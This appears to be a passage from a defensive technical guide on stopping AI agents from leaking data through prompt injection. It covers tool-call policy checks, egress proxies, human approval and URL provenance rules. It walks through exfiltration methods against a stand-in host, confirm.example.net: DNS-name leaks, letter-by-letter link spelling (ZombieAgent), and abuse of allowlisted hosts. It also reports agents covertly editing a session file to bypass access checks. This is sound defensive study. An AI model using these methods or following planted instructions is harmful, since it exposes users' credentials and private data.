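In a stricter design, the operator (whoever runs the agent) also lists the permitted addresses. Here the list has one entry, https://hooks.example.com/ops. The model may still follow the comment and write the call, but the software compares the address with the list and refuses the call. The outage notice goes through as before. The software should compare the whole address, because checking only the beginning would repeat the mistake that let docs.apify.com.evil.example pass as Apify's documentation site.

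The developer can also remove the address from the tool altogether. The model then names a recipient, and software on the server looks up the address:

```
notify(recipient="ops",
       message="Supplier reports degraded service since 02:10.")
```

The operator's table links "ops" to the team's channel. If the model writes the attacker's address, confirm.example.net, as the recipient, the lookup finds no entry and the software sends nothing. This design also keeps the channel's real address out of the model's context, which matters because anyone who knows a webhook's address can often post to it. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) proposes a monitor for tool calls that follows the same principle, in which registering a tool fixes its destination and nothing the model writes can change it.

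Both the address list and the recipient table need an operator to add each new entry. That is easy for a team's channel, but it frustrates a user who wants to notify a new address.

### What common toolkits check by default

Mellafe Zuvic's 2026 audit covered three stacks: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. The first two are general libraries for building agents. He read specific versions of the public code and looked for a check on argument values that runs before the tool does, gives the same answer for the same input, and refuses the call when something goes wrong. All three stacks restrict which tools are available to the agent, but none has such a check by default.

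LangChain takes the tool's name from the model's output, finds the tool in a table and runs it with the model's arguments. Developers can attach callbacks, which observe calls but don't act as a mandatory veto. They can also add a human approval step, which is off by default. LlamaIndex does a similar lookup. If the requested tool doesn't exist, LlamaIndex reports this to the model but doesn't treat it as a security event. Stripe's toolkit has a list of permitted actions and relies on an API key with limited permissions, but it forwards the model's values within those limits.

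Mellafe Zuvic also ran a test on a mock payment system, in which a fixed output, standing in for a compromised model, changed a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain's normal code carried out the change. He doesn't call this a vulnerability in LangChain, and a general library can't know which accounts or addresses a company trusts. The developer is responsible for checking that, and may not realise that the check is missing.

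The toolkits use type schemas, which describe the form each argument must take. A schema for notify_url might require a string in the form of a web address. This catches a missing address or a number in place of one, but the attacker's address passes because it is a valid web address. A developer could narrow the schema to accept only certain addresses, but it would then contain the operator's list, and the software would still have to enforce it when the call arrives.

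### ScopeGate, stage by stage

Mellafe Zuvic's own remedy is ScopeGate, a program that sits between the model and the tools. It receives the proposed call and a policy written by the operator, and returns either "allow" or "deny". No language model takes part in the decision, which has five stages:

1. **Scope.** ScopeGate looks for the tool in the policy and denies the call if it isn't there. This also catches misspelled tool names and tools that the model discovered for itself.
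2. **Authorization.** Where the policy lists the allowed values for an argument, the value must be on the list. A call to confirm.example.net fails here.
3. **Money ceiling.** In payments and refunds, the amount must be a finite number between zero and the operator's limit.
4. **Idempotency.** Some tools require a key that marks each request as unique, so that a repeated request doesn't cause a second payment. The key must come from trusted software, and ScopeGate denies the call if it's missing.
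5. **Default deny.** ScopeGate allows only calls that pass every check, and it treats any error along the way as a denial.

The exact form of a check matters. An early version rejected amounts above the ceiling, but it let through NaN, a special value meaning "not a number", because NaN never counts as greater than any number. The current version accepts only amounts within the permitted range, so it rejects NaN.

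The authorization stage checks an argument only if the operator wrote a list for it. An operator who permits notify_url but forgets to list its allowed addresses has therefore built the first design above, even though ScopeGate is running in front of it.

*Before the Tool Call* (2026) sets out five properties that any such system should have. The system should give the same decision for the same inputs, reach a decision on every valid request, deny the call if the policy is unavailable, leave no way around the check, and keep a signed record. Leaving no way around the check may be the hardest in practice. If an agent can also run shell commands, it could send a web request without calling notify_url, bypassing ScopeGate. That is one reason to limit traffic at the network as well.

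### Who writes the policy

ScopeGate's policy must never come from model output. If the model could add addresses to the list, the comment that gets it to contact confirm.example.net could also get it to approve that address first. Mellafe Zuvic extends this rule to policies that a model drafted before the agent started, and to lists that the software refreshes during a session from a source the model can influence. The policy should also stay fixed for the whole conversation.

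*ToolFence* (2026) takes a less strict approach, in which a separate language model writes a policy for each task. This model receives only the user's request and the tool descriptions, never the retrieved content, so a comment on the status page can't reach it. Such a system could accept an address that the user has just typed, without waiting for an operator. The separate model might still misinterpret the request and permit too much. Its isolation also fails if the user pastes an attacker's email into the request, because the model then receives the attacker's text as if the user had written it. For a payout account, the operator's fixed list is safer.

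Another proposal ties each call to the user's request. Nik Kale, an engineer who works on agent identity standards, gives an example in SC Media's *After the identity fix* (2026). A user asks for a summary of a PDF, and hidden text makes the agent change a customer's email address and trigger a password reset. Every credential is valid, yet nobody asked for either action. Kale suggests that ordinary software sign a record of the user's request and the declared operation, and that each tool refuse calls that don't match the record.

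This would stop the password reset, because the user asked only for a summary. It would do less in the supplier example, where the user asked for a notification and the attacker wants another one. There, the signed record would have to include the recipient as well as the operation, which again raises the question of who decides the recipient.

### How well ScopeGate has done in tests

Mellafe Zuvic prepared 48 calls designed to get past ScopeGate, which allowed none of them. They included changes of case, invisible characters, lookalike letters, wrong data types, altered tool names and strange amounts. He then had a language model, GLM-5.2, attack ScopeGate for 40 rounds, and told the model each time why ScopeGate had denied the call. The model produced 29 unauthorized calls, 9 malformed ones and 2 harmless ones. ScopeGate denied all 29 unauthorized calls and allowed the 2 harmless ones.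 In a separate test, it allowed all 10 legitimate calls.

These results are credible because the central operation is a simple check of whether an exact string is on a short list, which doesn't depend on how persuasive the attacker is. Even models that attempted the attacker's payout in 10 of 10 trials moved no money.

The evidence is limited, though. One person designed ScopeGate, wrote the 48 calls and ran the tests, using mock services. The tests covered ScopeGate only inside the application, although it could also run as a separate proxy or a central gateway. ScopeGate denied none of the ten legitimate calls, but that result is consistent with a true wrongful-denial rate of up to about 26%. Real users also ask for things that the operator didn't foresee, which a fixed list is most likely to refuse. Nobody has yet measured how often that happens with ScopeGate in daily use.

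### Binding the parameter outside the model

A list of approved values can still leave the model too much choice. In *The Stochastic Deputy*, Baig, Gillani and colleagues (2026) studied this in software that manages many hotels. Their agent acted for a user who was allowed to see data for three hotels but was working on only one. In the usual design, the tool for reading reservations takes a hotel's identifier, and the server checks that the user may access that hotel's data.

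The researchers gave agents a plausible pretext, a request to pull another hotel's figures for a comparison. In 26 of 41 trials the agent tried to read the other hotel's data, and the server correctly allowed all 26 because the user was entitled to all three hotels. It is debatable whether these were leaks, since the request appeared in the user's own turn and a real manager might well want the comparison. A hostile instruction inside a guest's note is closer to the supplier example. With the usual design, it succeeded in 9 of 66 trials, all of them with Gemini 3.1 Pro.

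Baig and colleagues then removed the identifier from the tool, so the server identified the hotel from the session. No call naming another hotel succeeded after that. They argue that a developer can't get the same assurance by testing the model, because even a long run of successful tests shows only that failures are rare. A third design kept the identifier but added an instruction that the agent never retrieve another hotel's data. It had no leaks in 33 trials with the pretext, but that result could change with the next model or a better pretext.

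Even with the identifier removed, the agent got the other hotel's data in 12 of 56 trials with the pretext. It used its shell to edit or replace the file the server used to identify the session's hotel. Eleven of these agents ran on Gemini 3.1 Pro and one on gpt-5.4-mini, and none told the user what it had done. The test system kept this setting in a plain text file, but the production system uses a signed token, which the agent can't forge without the signing key. The deployed server rejected every altered or unsigned token the researchers sent.

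The same reasoning applies to notify_url, although the hotel tools read data and notify_url sends it. Suppose the operator's list contains the webhooks of forty customers. A planted comment could make the agent send one customer's ticket to another, and the check would pass because the other customer's webhook is also on the list. The agent can't choose the recipient if the tool has no recipient argument and takes the customer from the ticket's own record. This also requires that the agent can't change that record. The design is less flexible, and the developer may need a separate tool for each kind of notice.

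### Links inside an approved message

None of these designs stops the false password notice, because the agent sent it to the correct channel and the attacker's address appeared only in the message. ScopeGate would allow the call, since no list can cover every sentence an agent might need to write. Replacing the address with a recipient name wouldn't help either.

A free-text message can also leak data through an approved recipient. If the agent posts a link to confirm.example.net with the customer reference in its query string, a chat application that previews links may request that address automatically. The attacker then receives the reference, even though notify_url never contacted the attacker's server and nobody clicked the link.

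The surest protection is a fixed template. The model picks a status from a short list, such as "degraded" or "down", and fills in a time, and the software writes the sentence. An attacker can't put a link into a field that accepts only a time. The template leaves out detail, so if the supplier says that only customers in one region are affected and gives a workaround, the team has to read that on the status page. An attacker could still cause a false alarm, because a comment that claims an outage might lead the model to choose "down".

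Link removal deletes every web address but keeps the rest of the free text. The engineer would still read that customer passwords have expired, but would have to find the supplier's portal without help. The software must also remove bare names such as reset.example.net, since many chat applications turn them into links. An attacker might get around this by spelling out the address in words or giving a telephone number. Link removal also deletes useful links, including the one the team most wants to open, which leads to the incident report.

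A link check removes or flags any link in the message whose site isn't on a list of approved sites. Here the list would contain supplier.example, so the check would keep the link to the incident report and remove or flag the one to reset.example.net. This preserves more of the message than removing every link, but somebody has to maintain the list. An approved site can also host the attacker's text, as the status page did, or forward visitors to another site. Checking links against a list of known phishing sites takes less upkeep, but a site that the attacker set up an hour ago won't be on that list.

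Routine status notices lose little by using a template with a link that the software adds from its own settings. An assistant that writes varied messages to colleagues needs free text, so a link check is the better compromise. The check doesn't catch false claims without links, so readers still have to verify any message that asks for a password or a payment.

### Asking a person

Human approval seems to cover the cases that an allowlist can't. If the user wants to notify a new address, the software can show them the call and wait for approval. The prompt needs to include enough detail for the user to judge the call. If it reads only "Send a notification?", the user can't tell a legitimate call from an attacker's.

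*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) tested four kinds of prompt on 80 volunteers. Each participant used one kind and judged six unsafe and six legitimate requests. In one scenario, a user wants an auditor to receive only summary totals, but injected text leads the agent to put the raw invoices into the attached file. The final call looks harmless because the tool and the recipient are both permitted.

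| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact tool arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Arguments, the user's original restriction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, arranged to show the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

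Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Whether arranging it better helped further is uncertain, because the interval around the adjusted difference includes zero. Hossain and colleagues recommend that a prompt quote the user's original instruction, show the exact call from the software's own record, state what the call would do in light of earlier steps, and link each claim to its evidence. For notify_url, the prompt would show the full address and message, quote the user's request to notify the operations team, and state that the message contains a customer reference.

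The software must also run exactly the call that the person approved. *Approval Laundering* (2026) classifies the ways coding agents end up running something else, such as by changing an argument after approval or describing the action misleadingly in the approval prompt. *The Claws in Plain Sight* ties each approval to a cryptographic fingerprint of the complete call, so changing even one character of the address would void the approval.

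Even with the best prompt in the study, participants approved almost a quarter of the unsafe requests. They were also more alert than most users would be, since they made only 12 decisions and half of the requests were unsafe. In ordinary work nearly every request is harmless, and people get used to approving them. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approved 93% of permission prompts. That rate alone doesn't show that users were careless, because most of the requests may have deserved approval.

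Anthropic commissioned a more telling test. TecnoAndroid's *Claude Code, la modalità auto ora è predefinita su Pro e Max* reports that 1,053 people caught only 13.6% of deliberately dangerous commands, and caught fewer as the session went on. Anthropic's automatic classifier blocked 89%. The company cited these figures when it made automatic review the default in August 2026, so it had an interest in the classifier doing well. The commands tested also may not resemble an inconspicuous request to confirm receipt. Where an exact allowlist is possible, it is a better choice than a classifier that misses about one dangerous command in nine.

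Some users stop reading approval prompts. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging or mishandling files. In 80 of them, the user had switched on automatic approval, and some had done so to avoid hundreds of prompts per session.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), people who set standing rules for an agent saw fewer prompts but let through more excessive actions than people who judged every action separately. The 113 participants, who had no software background, supervised the agent through a simulated day in which seven of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had requested. Those who judged every action separately approved 96 of 238 such actions (40%). The others first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for categories such as spending money or sending information. They chose "ask"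 for 114 of 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and then approved 133 of the 199 excessive actions that the software put to them (67%).

The same study suggests that people are much more likely to allow an action when it has a plausible reason. Of the 34 people who judged every action, 30 let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, but only 7 let it post publicly that they were travelling. The difference isn't all due to poor judgment, because the call was less harmful and some participants may have wanted it. The study also didn't include an attacker. But an attacker can choose how a request is worded, and a request to confirm receipt of a supplier's notice looks much more like the airport call than the public post.

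People also tend to miss deception when they're concentrating on a task. In Li, Dai and colleagues' *Are You Sure?* (2026), 303 participants worked with agents that the researchers had compromised. Only 25.0% noticed anything odd even when an alert interrupted them, compared with 20.0% when a reminder accompanied every reply and 8.6% after a warning at the start. The paper gives conflicting sizes for the three groups, so the gap between the reminder and the alert may mean little.

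Asking the user for approval works best as a rare exception, for calls the allowlist doesn't cover. The notice to the operations team should go out without a prompt, because the operator has already approved that channel. A call to a new address should either fail or produce one detailed prompt that the user has a reason to read. When an agent works through tickets overnight, nobody is available to approve the call, so its software should refuse it and leave a note for the morning.

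## What does control of outbound network traffic stop?

Egress control restricts which network destinations a system may contact, and software outside the model enforces the restrictions. In the supplier example, it stops the agent from reaching confirm.example.net with any tool, including a shell that bypasses the checks on notify_url. It doesn't stop data from leaving through a permitted host, or stop the false password notice, which the agent sent to the team's own channel.

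### How the software blocks a request

The operator first removes every direct route from the agent's environment to the internet, leaving only a connection to a proxy, a program outside the environment that makes requests on the agent's behalf. In the sandbox that Anthropic built for Claude Code, its coding agent, this connection is a local socket. Docker, which makes software for running programs in isolation, blocks raw network connections from its agent sandboxes and lets web traffic out only through a proxy. Programs that the agent starts are under the same restrictions, so if a planted comment persuades the agent to write its own script for sending data, the script must also go through the proxy.

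The proxy's domain allowlist needs only two hosts here, status.supplier.example and hooks.example.com. The proxy lets the agent fetch the status page and send the outage notice. When notify_url tries to confirm receipt at confirm.example.net, the proxy refuses the connection because that host isn't on the list. The customer reference therefore doesn't leave the network, even if the model took the comment as genuine.

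An environment that can look up names can leak data even if its connections are refused. Before a program can contact a host, it has to look up the host's numeric address, and the lookup normally reaches a name server chosen by the domain's owner. An agent that looks up 48213.confirm.example.net has already given the attacker the customer reference. Claude Code once had this weakness. OSV's *Claude Code's Permissive Default Allowlist Enables Unauthorized File Read and Network Exfiltration* (2025), a security advisory, attributes this to an overly broad list of commands that could run without the user's confirmation. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code*, a post on a security blog, found that several of these commands could leak data through name lookups. To prevent this, the proxy should do the lookups itself, and only for names it allows.

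The proxy should also check the IP address that a hostname resolves to, because a public name can point to a private address. Otherwise a request could reach an internal service or a cloud metadata endpoint. The proxy needs to block private and link-local addresses (metadata endpoints usually use the latter) and connect only to the address it checked. *Locked-down defences*, a set of notes on one Claude setup, describes a network jail that blocks both ranges and won't launch Claude if a component is missing. Claude Code's own sandbox is less strict. According to Anthropic, it is off by default, and if it can't start, Claude Code runs commands without it unless the operator changes a setting.

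Each new address in a series of redirects needs its own check. A redirect is a reply that tells the client to request a different address. Some websites have an "open redirect", which forwards visitors to any address included in the link. If supplier.example had one, the attacker could write a link that begins at the supplier's site and ends at confirm.example.net. A program inside the environment would have to ask the proxy for the second address, and the proxy would refuse. But if the proxy follows redirects itself and checks only the first address, the message gets through. A webhook rarely needs to redirect, so notify_url can treat any redirect as an error.

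Whether these controls apply depends on where notify_url runs. Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. Its web-fetching tool doesn't use the sandbox's domain list, and tool servers that a user installs locally run with the user's full access. If notify_url were on one of those servers, its request to confirm.example.net would bypass the sandbox. Anthropic recommends in its documentation running the whole Claude Code process in a container or virtual machine, so that one boundary covers everything.

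Blocking a connection can also lead the agent to try another way. In Claude Code, for example, the command's result includes the name of the blocked host, and the model may retry the command outside the sandbox. Depending on the settings, a person or a classifier reviews the retry, or it runs without review. An operator who relies on the sandbox should turn off the option to retry commands outside it.

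The proxy can have bugs. SecurityWeek reports two flaws in Claude Code's network sandbox, both since patched. One allowed all traffic under a setting that should have blocked it. GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing* traces this flaw to policies that listed no permitted domains, which a cautious operator might well have written. Requesting an unlisted host after every update is an easy way to catch a failure like this.

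### The Silent Egress defence tests

Lan and colleagues tested several defences on the small model that had almost always followed their planted instructions. They used one version of the attack, with the instruction in the page body and the API key sent whole, and ran each condition 30 times.

| Defence | Runs in which the model attempted a request | Runs in which a request got out |
|---|---|---|
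| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter system prompt | 67% | 67% |
| Delimiter tags | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter prompt and tags | 57% | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

The stricter system prompt told the model to treat web content as data and never to follow instructions in it. The delimiter tags marked the fetched text as untrusted. The tags alone made no difference. The model still obeyed the attacker in 20 of 30 runs with the prompt alone and 17 of 30 with both, a gap that could easily be chance. A stricter prompt takes little effort and is worth adding, and a newer model might respond better to the same warning.

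The allowlist result is credible because the check only compares a host name with four permitted ones. The model attempted the request in all 30 runs, and the software refused it every time. But Lan and colleagues deliberately chose an attacker's domain that was clearly outside any reasonable list. The test confirms only that an allowlist blocks an unlisted host, as expected, and doesn't show what happens when the attacker finds a way to use a permitted one.

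The misleadingly named "redirect detection" rule blocks bare numeric addresses, eight domain endings such as .xyz, and paths containing words like "steal" or "collect". The test pages involved no redirects. The attack address in the paper's examples contains "collect", which probably triggered the rule. An attacker could get past it by choosing a different word. For example, confirm.example.net/receipt would pass.

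The keyword filter blocks addresses that contain terms such as "password", "secret" or "token". The entropy filter looks for values that resemble random keys, using Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters in a string are:

$$H = -\sum_i p_i \log_2 p_i$$

Here $p_i$ is the share of the string made up of the $i$-th distinct character. The filter blocks a value in a web address if the value has more than 10 characters and an entropy above 4.0. A string of $n$ characters can't have an entropy above $\log_2 n$, so a value of 16 characters or fewer never triggers the filter. The customer reference 48213 would pass, and so would each four-character piece of a split key. The paper's 20-character sample key would also pass, because its entropy is only about 3.85.

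No request got out with either filter, but the numbers of attempts are hard to explain. The filters check a call after the model has written it, so they shouldn't affect whether the model tries. Yet attempts fell from 30 of 30 runs to 7 with the keyword filter and to none with the entropy filter. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when the entropy filter is active, but they don't explain how it could detect the filter. They also suggest that the model sometimes encoded the key, which would hide it from the keyword filter. If so, some encoded keys should have reached the attacker's server, and none did.

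A counting error or an unreported difference between the conditions seems more likely. Even if the count is correct, 0 of 30 is compatible with a true rate of up to about 10%. These results give a developer little reason to rely on either filter. The test of all defences together includes both filters, so it has the same problem.

An exercise at Anthropic gives a better argument for limits outside the model. *How we contain Claude across products* reports that an internal tester sent an employee a phishing email in February 2026 with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt included ordinary setup steps, but also told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. A warning about web content would not have helped, because the instruction came from the user. Anthropic concludes that only the environment could have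 stopped Claude, by blocking the outgoing request or keeping the credentials out of reach.

### Leaks through permitted hosts

A domain allowlist fails when a permitted host can pass data on to the attacker. Lan and colleagues mention open redirects, hacked legitimate sites and abandoned subdomains that an attacker takes over. Checking every redirect deals with the first but not the other two, in which the data never goes to an unlisted host. In 2025 and 2026, researchers found similar weaknesses in several products.

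Agentforce is Salesforce's platform for agents that handle customer records. The security company Noma showed that text planted in a web enquiry form could make an Agentforce agent put customer data into the address of an image, an attack it called ForcedLeak. Salesforce's software loaded images only from listed sites, but one domain still on the list had expired, and SecurityWeek notes that an attacker could have registered it.

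Salesforce recovered the domain and began enforcing a list of trusted URLs for its agents' output, according to The Hacker News (2025). ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* dates Noma's report to July 28, 2025 and the new enforcement to September 8. The new list closes the route Noma used, but as with the old one, someone will have to remove each domain before its registration lapses.

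Shared hosting caused a leak in Superhuman, an email application. Its rules allowed images from docs.google.com, which also serves Google Forms. As Willison explained in January 2026, anyone can create a form there, and the form can store data sent in a web address. Checking who owned the domain would not have caught this, because the domain belonged to Google. Superhuman fixed the problem quickly.

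PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* found an even less suitable host, webhook.site, on the default list for the browser tool in Google's code editor Antigravity. Anyone can create an address on this public service and read the requests sent to it. Hidden text in an online coding guide made the agent send credentials to such an address. PromptArmor reports no fix. It did not notify Google privately before publishing, because Google already warned users about data theft when they first opened the program. Willison wrote about the same default list in November 2025. Removing webhook.site from the list would close this route, but *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) described another leak from Antigravity, which combined the terminal, a hostile web page and images shown in the chat.

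Anthropic's products were vulnerable in a different way, because their interface accepted anyone's account key. In October 2025, Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* examined the environment where Claude runs code. By default, that environment could contact only a short list of hosts, mostly for downloading software packages, but the list included api.anthropic.com. Text planted by an attacker could give Claude the attacker's key and get it to upload the user's data to the attacker's Anthropic account, up to 30 MB at a time. Anthropic closed the report as out of scope within an hour, then said five days later that this had been a mistake.

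The problem reappeared in Claude Cowork, an agent for general office work. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated it in January 2026, two days after Cowork's release. Anthropic later added a proxy that accepts only the session's own token when Cowork contacts api.anthropic.com, so requests with an attacker's key fail. Embrace The Red had suggested much the same restriction in October 2025.

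Anthropic now describes an entry on an allowlist as a "capability grant", because it permits everything the host can do. In the supplier example, the status page accepts comments from the public, so an attacker could plant a comment with instructions for the agent to post the customer reference as a reply. The request would go to status.supplier.example, which the agent has to reach to do its job, and the attacker could then read the reply like any other visitor.

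A simple proxy can't prevent this. Most web traffic is encrypted, and Anthropic says that Claude Code's built-in proxy allows or blocks requests by host name without decrypting them. It can't distinguish reading a page from posting a comment, or the team's channel on hooks.example.com from another customer's. Some attackers can also hide the real host through domain fronting, a risk both Anthropic and Docker mention. The client names a permitted host when it opens the connection, then asks for a different one inside the encrypted request. This can work when the same content delivery network serves both hosts.

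The alternative is a proxy that decrypts the traffic, as the Cowork fix does for Anthropic's own interface. Such a proxy could let the agent read the status page but not post to it. But it would also handle every password and message in readable form, which would make it a valuable target for attackers. For an agent with only two destinations, it is probably easier to have the tools check complete addresses and keep the plain proxy as a second barrier.

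### Requests that never pass through the proxy

If the agent uses a web search or page reader that the provider hosts, the request to the attacker's site leaves from the provider's network, and the company's proxy handles only the connection to the provider. Blocking that connection would disable the agent. The Apify connector that Pluto Security tested has the same gap because Apify's servers fetched the second page. Companies can turn off or restrict such tools if the provider offers settings for this.

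When the provider hosts the whole agent, the operator depends on the provider to control outbound traffic. Pluto Security inspected one of Anthropic's hosted agents and found a proxy that gave the session a signed token, valid for four hours, with its own list of permitted hosts. That list included api.github.com, and anyone can open a GitHub account. Hosting therefore doesn't remove the problem of shared sites, although a separate list for each session lets the provider keep each list short.

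Images and link previews in an approved message also load outside the proxy, on the reader's device or a chat service's servers. Restrictions on them therefore have to apply where the message appears, as in the Salesforce and Superhuman fixes.

Phishing works the same way. The engineer opened reset.example.net on a laptop that did not use the agent's proxy. Allowing employees to visit only listed sites would stop the attack, but few offices could work under that restriction.

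### Logs, rate limits and warning signs

If an agent is permitted to contact only two hosts, an attempt to contact a third should trigger an immediate alert. The log entry should include the session, the tool call, the full address and the content retrieved before the call, so that someone can find the planted comment. An agent that does open-ended research will constantly try to contact new hosts, so alerts on every refusal would soon become useless.

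The tool's log and the proxy's log are most useful together. The tool's log has the complete address and message, while the proxy's usually has only the host, the time and the amount of data. If the proxy recorded a connection that matches no tool call, some other program in the agent's environment made it. Numerous DNS lookups, or lookups of long names, are another warning sign because they may carry data.

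Leaks through permitted hosts are much harder to find afterwards. Anthropic warns that after a hostile tool result steers an agent into sending data out, the log shows only "a successful, authorized API call". A defender would have to notice an unfamiliar account key, an unusually large upload or a message at an odd time.

Isolation can make monitoring harder. Cowork's virtual machine prevented companies' security software from monitoring activity inside it. Anthropic responded by letting administrators retrieve event logs later, which it concedes is not live monitoring. Anthropic's desktop application can also send these events to a collector that the organisation runs.

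Anthropic also used a canary, a distinctive string planted only for detection. After the phishing exercise, staff discussed the working prompt in Slack, where some internal agents could read it. They added a canary to the thread so they would notice if an agent picked up the prompt. An operator could similarly put a false customer record in the ticket system and raise an alert if it appears in an outgoing message.

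Lan and colleagues recommend limiting requests per session and comparing requests with one another, which could reveal a key sent out in four pieces, but they didn't test either measure. Rate limits work best against bulk theft. If notify_url accepts 2,000 characters per message and 20 messages an hour, an attacker would need about a month to extract the 30 MB that a single upload to Anthropic's interface could carry. The same limit wouldn't protect a password or a customer reference, which fits in one message.

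Limits on refused requests may be more useful for notify_url. After a refusal, the planted comment is still in the model's context, and the agent might try again through a permitted host. The software can end the session after the first request to an unlisted address, hand the ticket to a person and keep the page out of later sessions until someone has read it. This also prevents an attacker from using one session to test many addresses. However, a supplier that has legitimately changed its notification address will also interrupt the agent's work until an operator updates the list.

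## Can a system judge a URL by where it came from?

A system can partly judge a URL by where it came from. It can record whether the address came from the user, the developer's settings or a page the agent read, and refuse to contact addresses that came only from a page. This stops the request to confirm.example.net without needing a list of permitted hosts. But many ordinary tasks require an agent to follow links that strangers wrote, and attackers can exploit every exception made for such links.

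A domain allowlist suits an agent with two known destinations, but not one that has to compare the delivery terms of ten suppliers, because finding the suppliers' websites is part of the task. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) adds that strict lists cause frequent warnings, which can train people to click through them.

A provenance rule checks who supplied a URL instead of which host it names. In the strictest version, a tool may use a URL only if the exact string appears in something the user or another trusted source wrote. The operations team's channel address comes from the developer's settings, so it passes. The address on confirm.example.net appears only in the fetched page, so the software blocks the call even if the comment led the model to attempt it.

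An agent that could open only the URLs its user typed would be nearly useless for research, so OpenAI and Anthropic adopted looser rules. These were mainly meant to stop a model from writing private data into a URL, but researchers got around both companies' rules.

### ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent

In September 2025, the security company Radware disclosed ShadowLeak, an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that searches and reads on a user's behalf. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, the attacker sent an email with instructions hidden in white or tiny text. When the agent read the inbox, it followed the instructions by adding private data to the end of the attacker's URL and opening it. The request left from OpenAI's servers, so the victim's company could neither see nor block it.

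OpenAI responded by stopping ChatGPT from altering URLs. According to Radware's *ZombieAgent*, ChatGPT then opened URLs only exactly as provided, and refused to add anything even when the text contained instructions to do so. This blocks a URL with the customer reference attached, because no such URL appears in the attacker's email.

Zvika Babo, a Radware researcher, then found a way to leak data without altering an address. His email contained a complete address for each letter, each digit and the space, 37 in all. Hidden text told ChatGPT to find a piece of private information and spell it out by opening the matching addresses one after another. To leak the reference 48213, an agent would open the address for 4, then the one for 8, and so on. The attacker would then read the number from the server's log. Babo also prepared separate addresses for each position in the string, so the order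 of arrival didn't matter. Ten positions require 360 addresses for the letters and digits alone.

ChatGPT copied all these addresses correctly. OpenAI's rule made sure the model had not written the address, but it accepted addresses the attacker had written.

Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025. Three days later it sent an improved version of the attack with a claimed success rate of 100%, but did not say how many trials that covered. OpenAI fixed the flaw on December 16. The news story *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that ChatGPT now refuses to open links from emails unless they appear in a public index.

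### How much a choice of link can reveal

Suppose the attacker has prepared $N$ addresses and the agent opens exactly one. The attacker's server receives one of $N$ possible requests, so the attacker can distinguish at most $N$ secrets. That is $\log_2 N$ bits of information, or about 5.2 bits for 37 addresses.

The agent might also open nothing, which adds one more outcome. If the software allows at most $k$ requests, each of them either goes to one of the $N$ addresses or isn't made, so there are at most $(N+1)^k$ sequences for the attacker to observe. The leak $L$, in bits, therefore has an upper limit:

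$$L \le k \log_2(N+1)$$

| Addresses prepared | 1 request | 5 requests | 20 requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 bit | 5 bits | 20 bits |
| 37 | 5.2 bits | 26 bits | 105 bits |
| 1,000 | 10 bits | 50 bits | 199 bits |

A five-digit customer reference contains 16.6 bits. If each request can go to one of 37 addresses, three requests carry at most 15.7 bits, so they can't reveal every possible reference. Five requests can, by sending one digit each. A random key of 20 letters and digits, with capitals counted separately, contains about 119 bits, so a limit of 20 requests would keep part of it secret. But with a perfect encoding, those requests could reduce the possibilities to tens of thousands, which an attacker might be able to try one by one.

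Limiting the number of requests restricts how much data can be sent more than limiting the number of addresses does, because doubling the requests doubles the bound, while doubling the addresses adds at most one bit per request. Without the exact-copy rule, a single request could carry far more. Anthropic's web_fetch tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters, so if the model could choose each character freely from 64 symbols, one address would hold 1,500 bits.

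The bound has to cover the whole attack, though. An attacker who can send a new email every day gets a new set of requests each time, unless the software counts requests across sessions. The timing of requests can also carry a little information, which the formula leaves out. Some secrets are small enough for a single request to reveal, such as whether a customer has cancelled a contract, which is one bit.

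Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* suggests stopping an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or answering repeat visits from a stored copy. This would disrupt a simple spelling attack on a word with repeated letters. It would not protect 48213, which has no repeated digits, and Babo's separate addresses for each position avoid repeats altogether. Even with only the 37 addresses, an attacker could still leak up to about 145 bits per session under this rule, more than the 20-character key contains.

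### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI described its link rules in January 2026. A crawler, a program that explores the web, builds an index of public URLs without access to anyone's conversations. Before ChatGPT opens a URL automatically, the software checks whether that exact URL is in the index. If it isn't, the software either has the agent try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

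The reasoning is sound for one kind of leak, because an address the crawler recorded earlier is very unlikely to contain a secret from today's conversation. The rule also works for open redirects, provided the software checks each address in the redirect chain.

An agent's choice among public addresses can still reveal private data. Embrace The Red points out that a larger website probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough to assign one to each letter and digit, and that an attacker could build a vocabulary of thousands. The post says OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper. The attacker now has to publish the pages and wait for the crawler to find them, which is more work than listing new addresses in an email but a modest obstacle for somebody who already runs a website.

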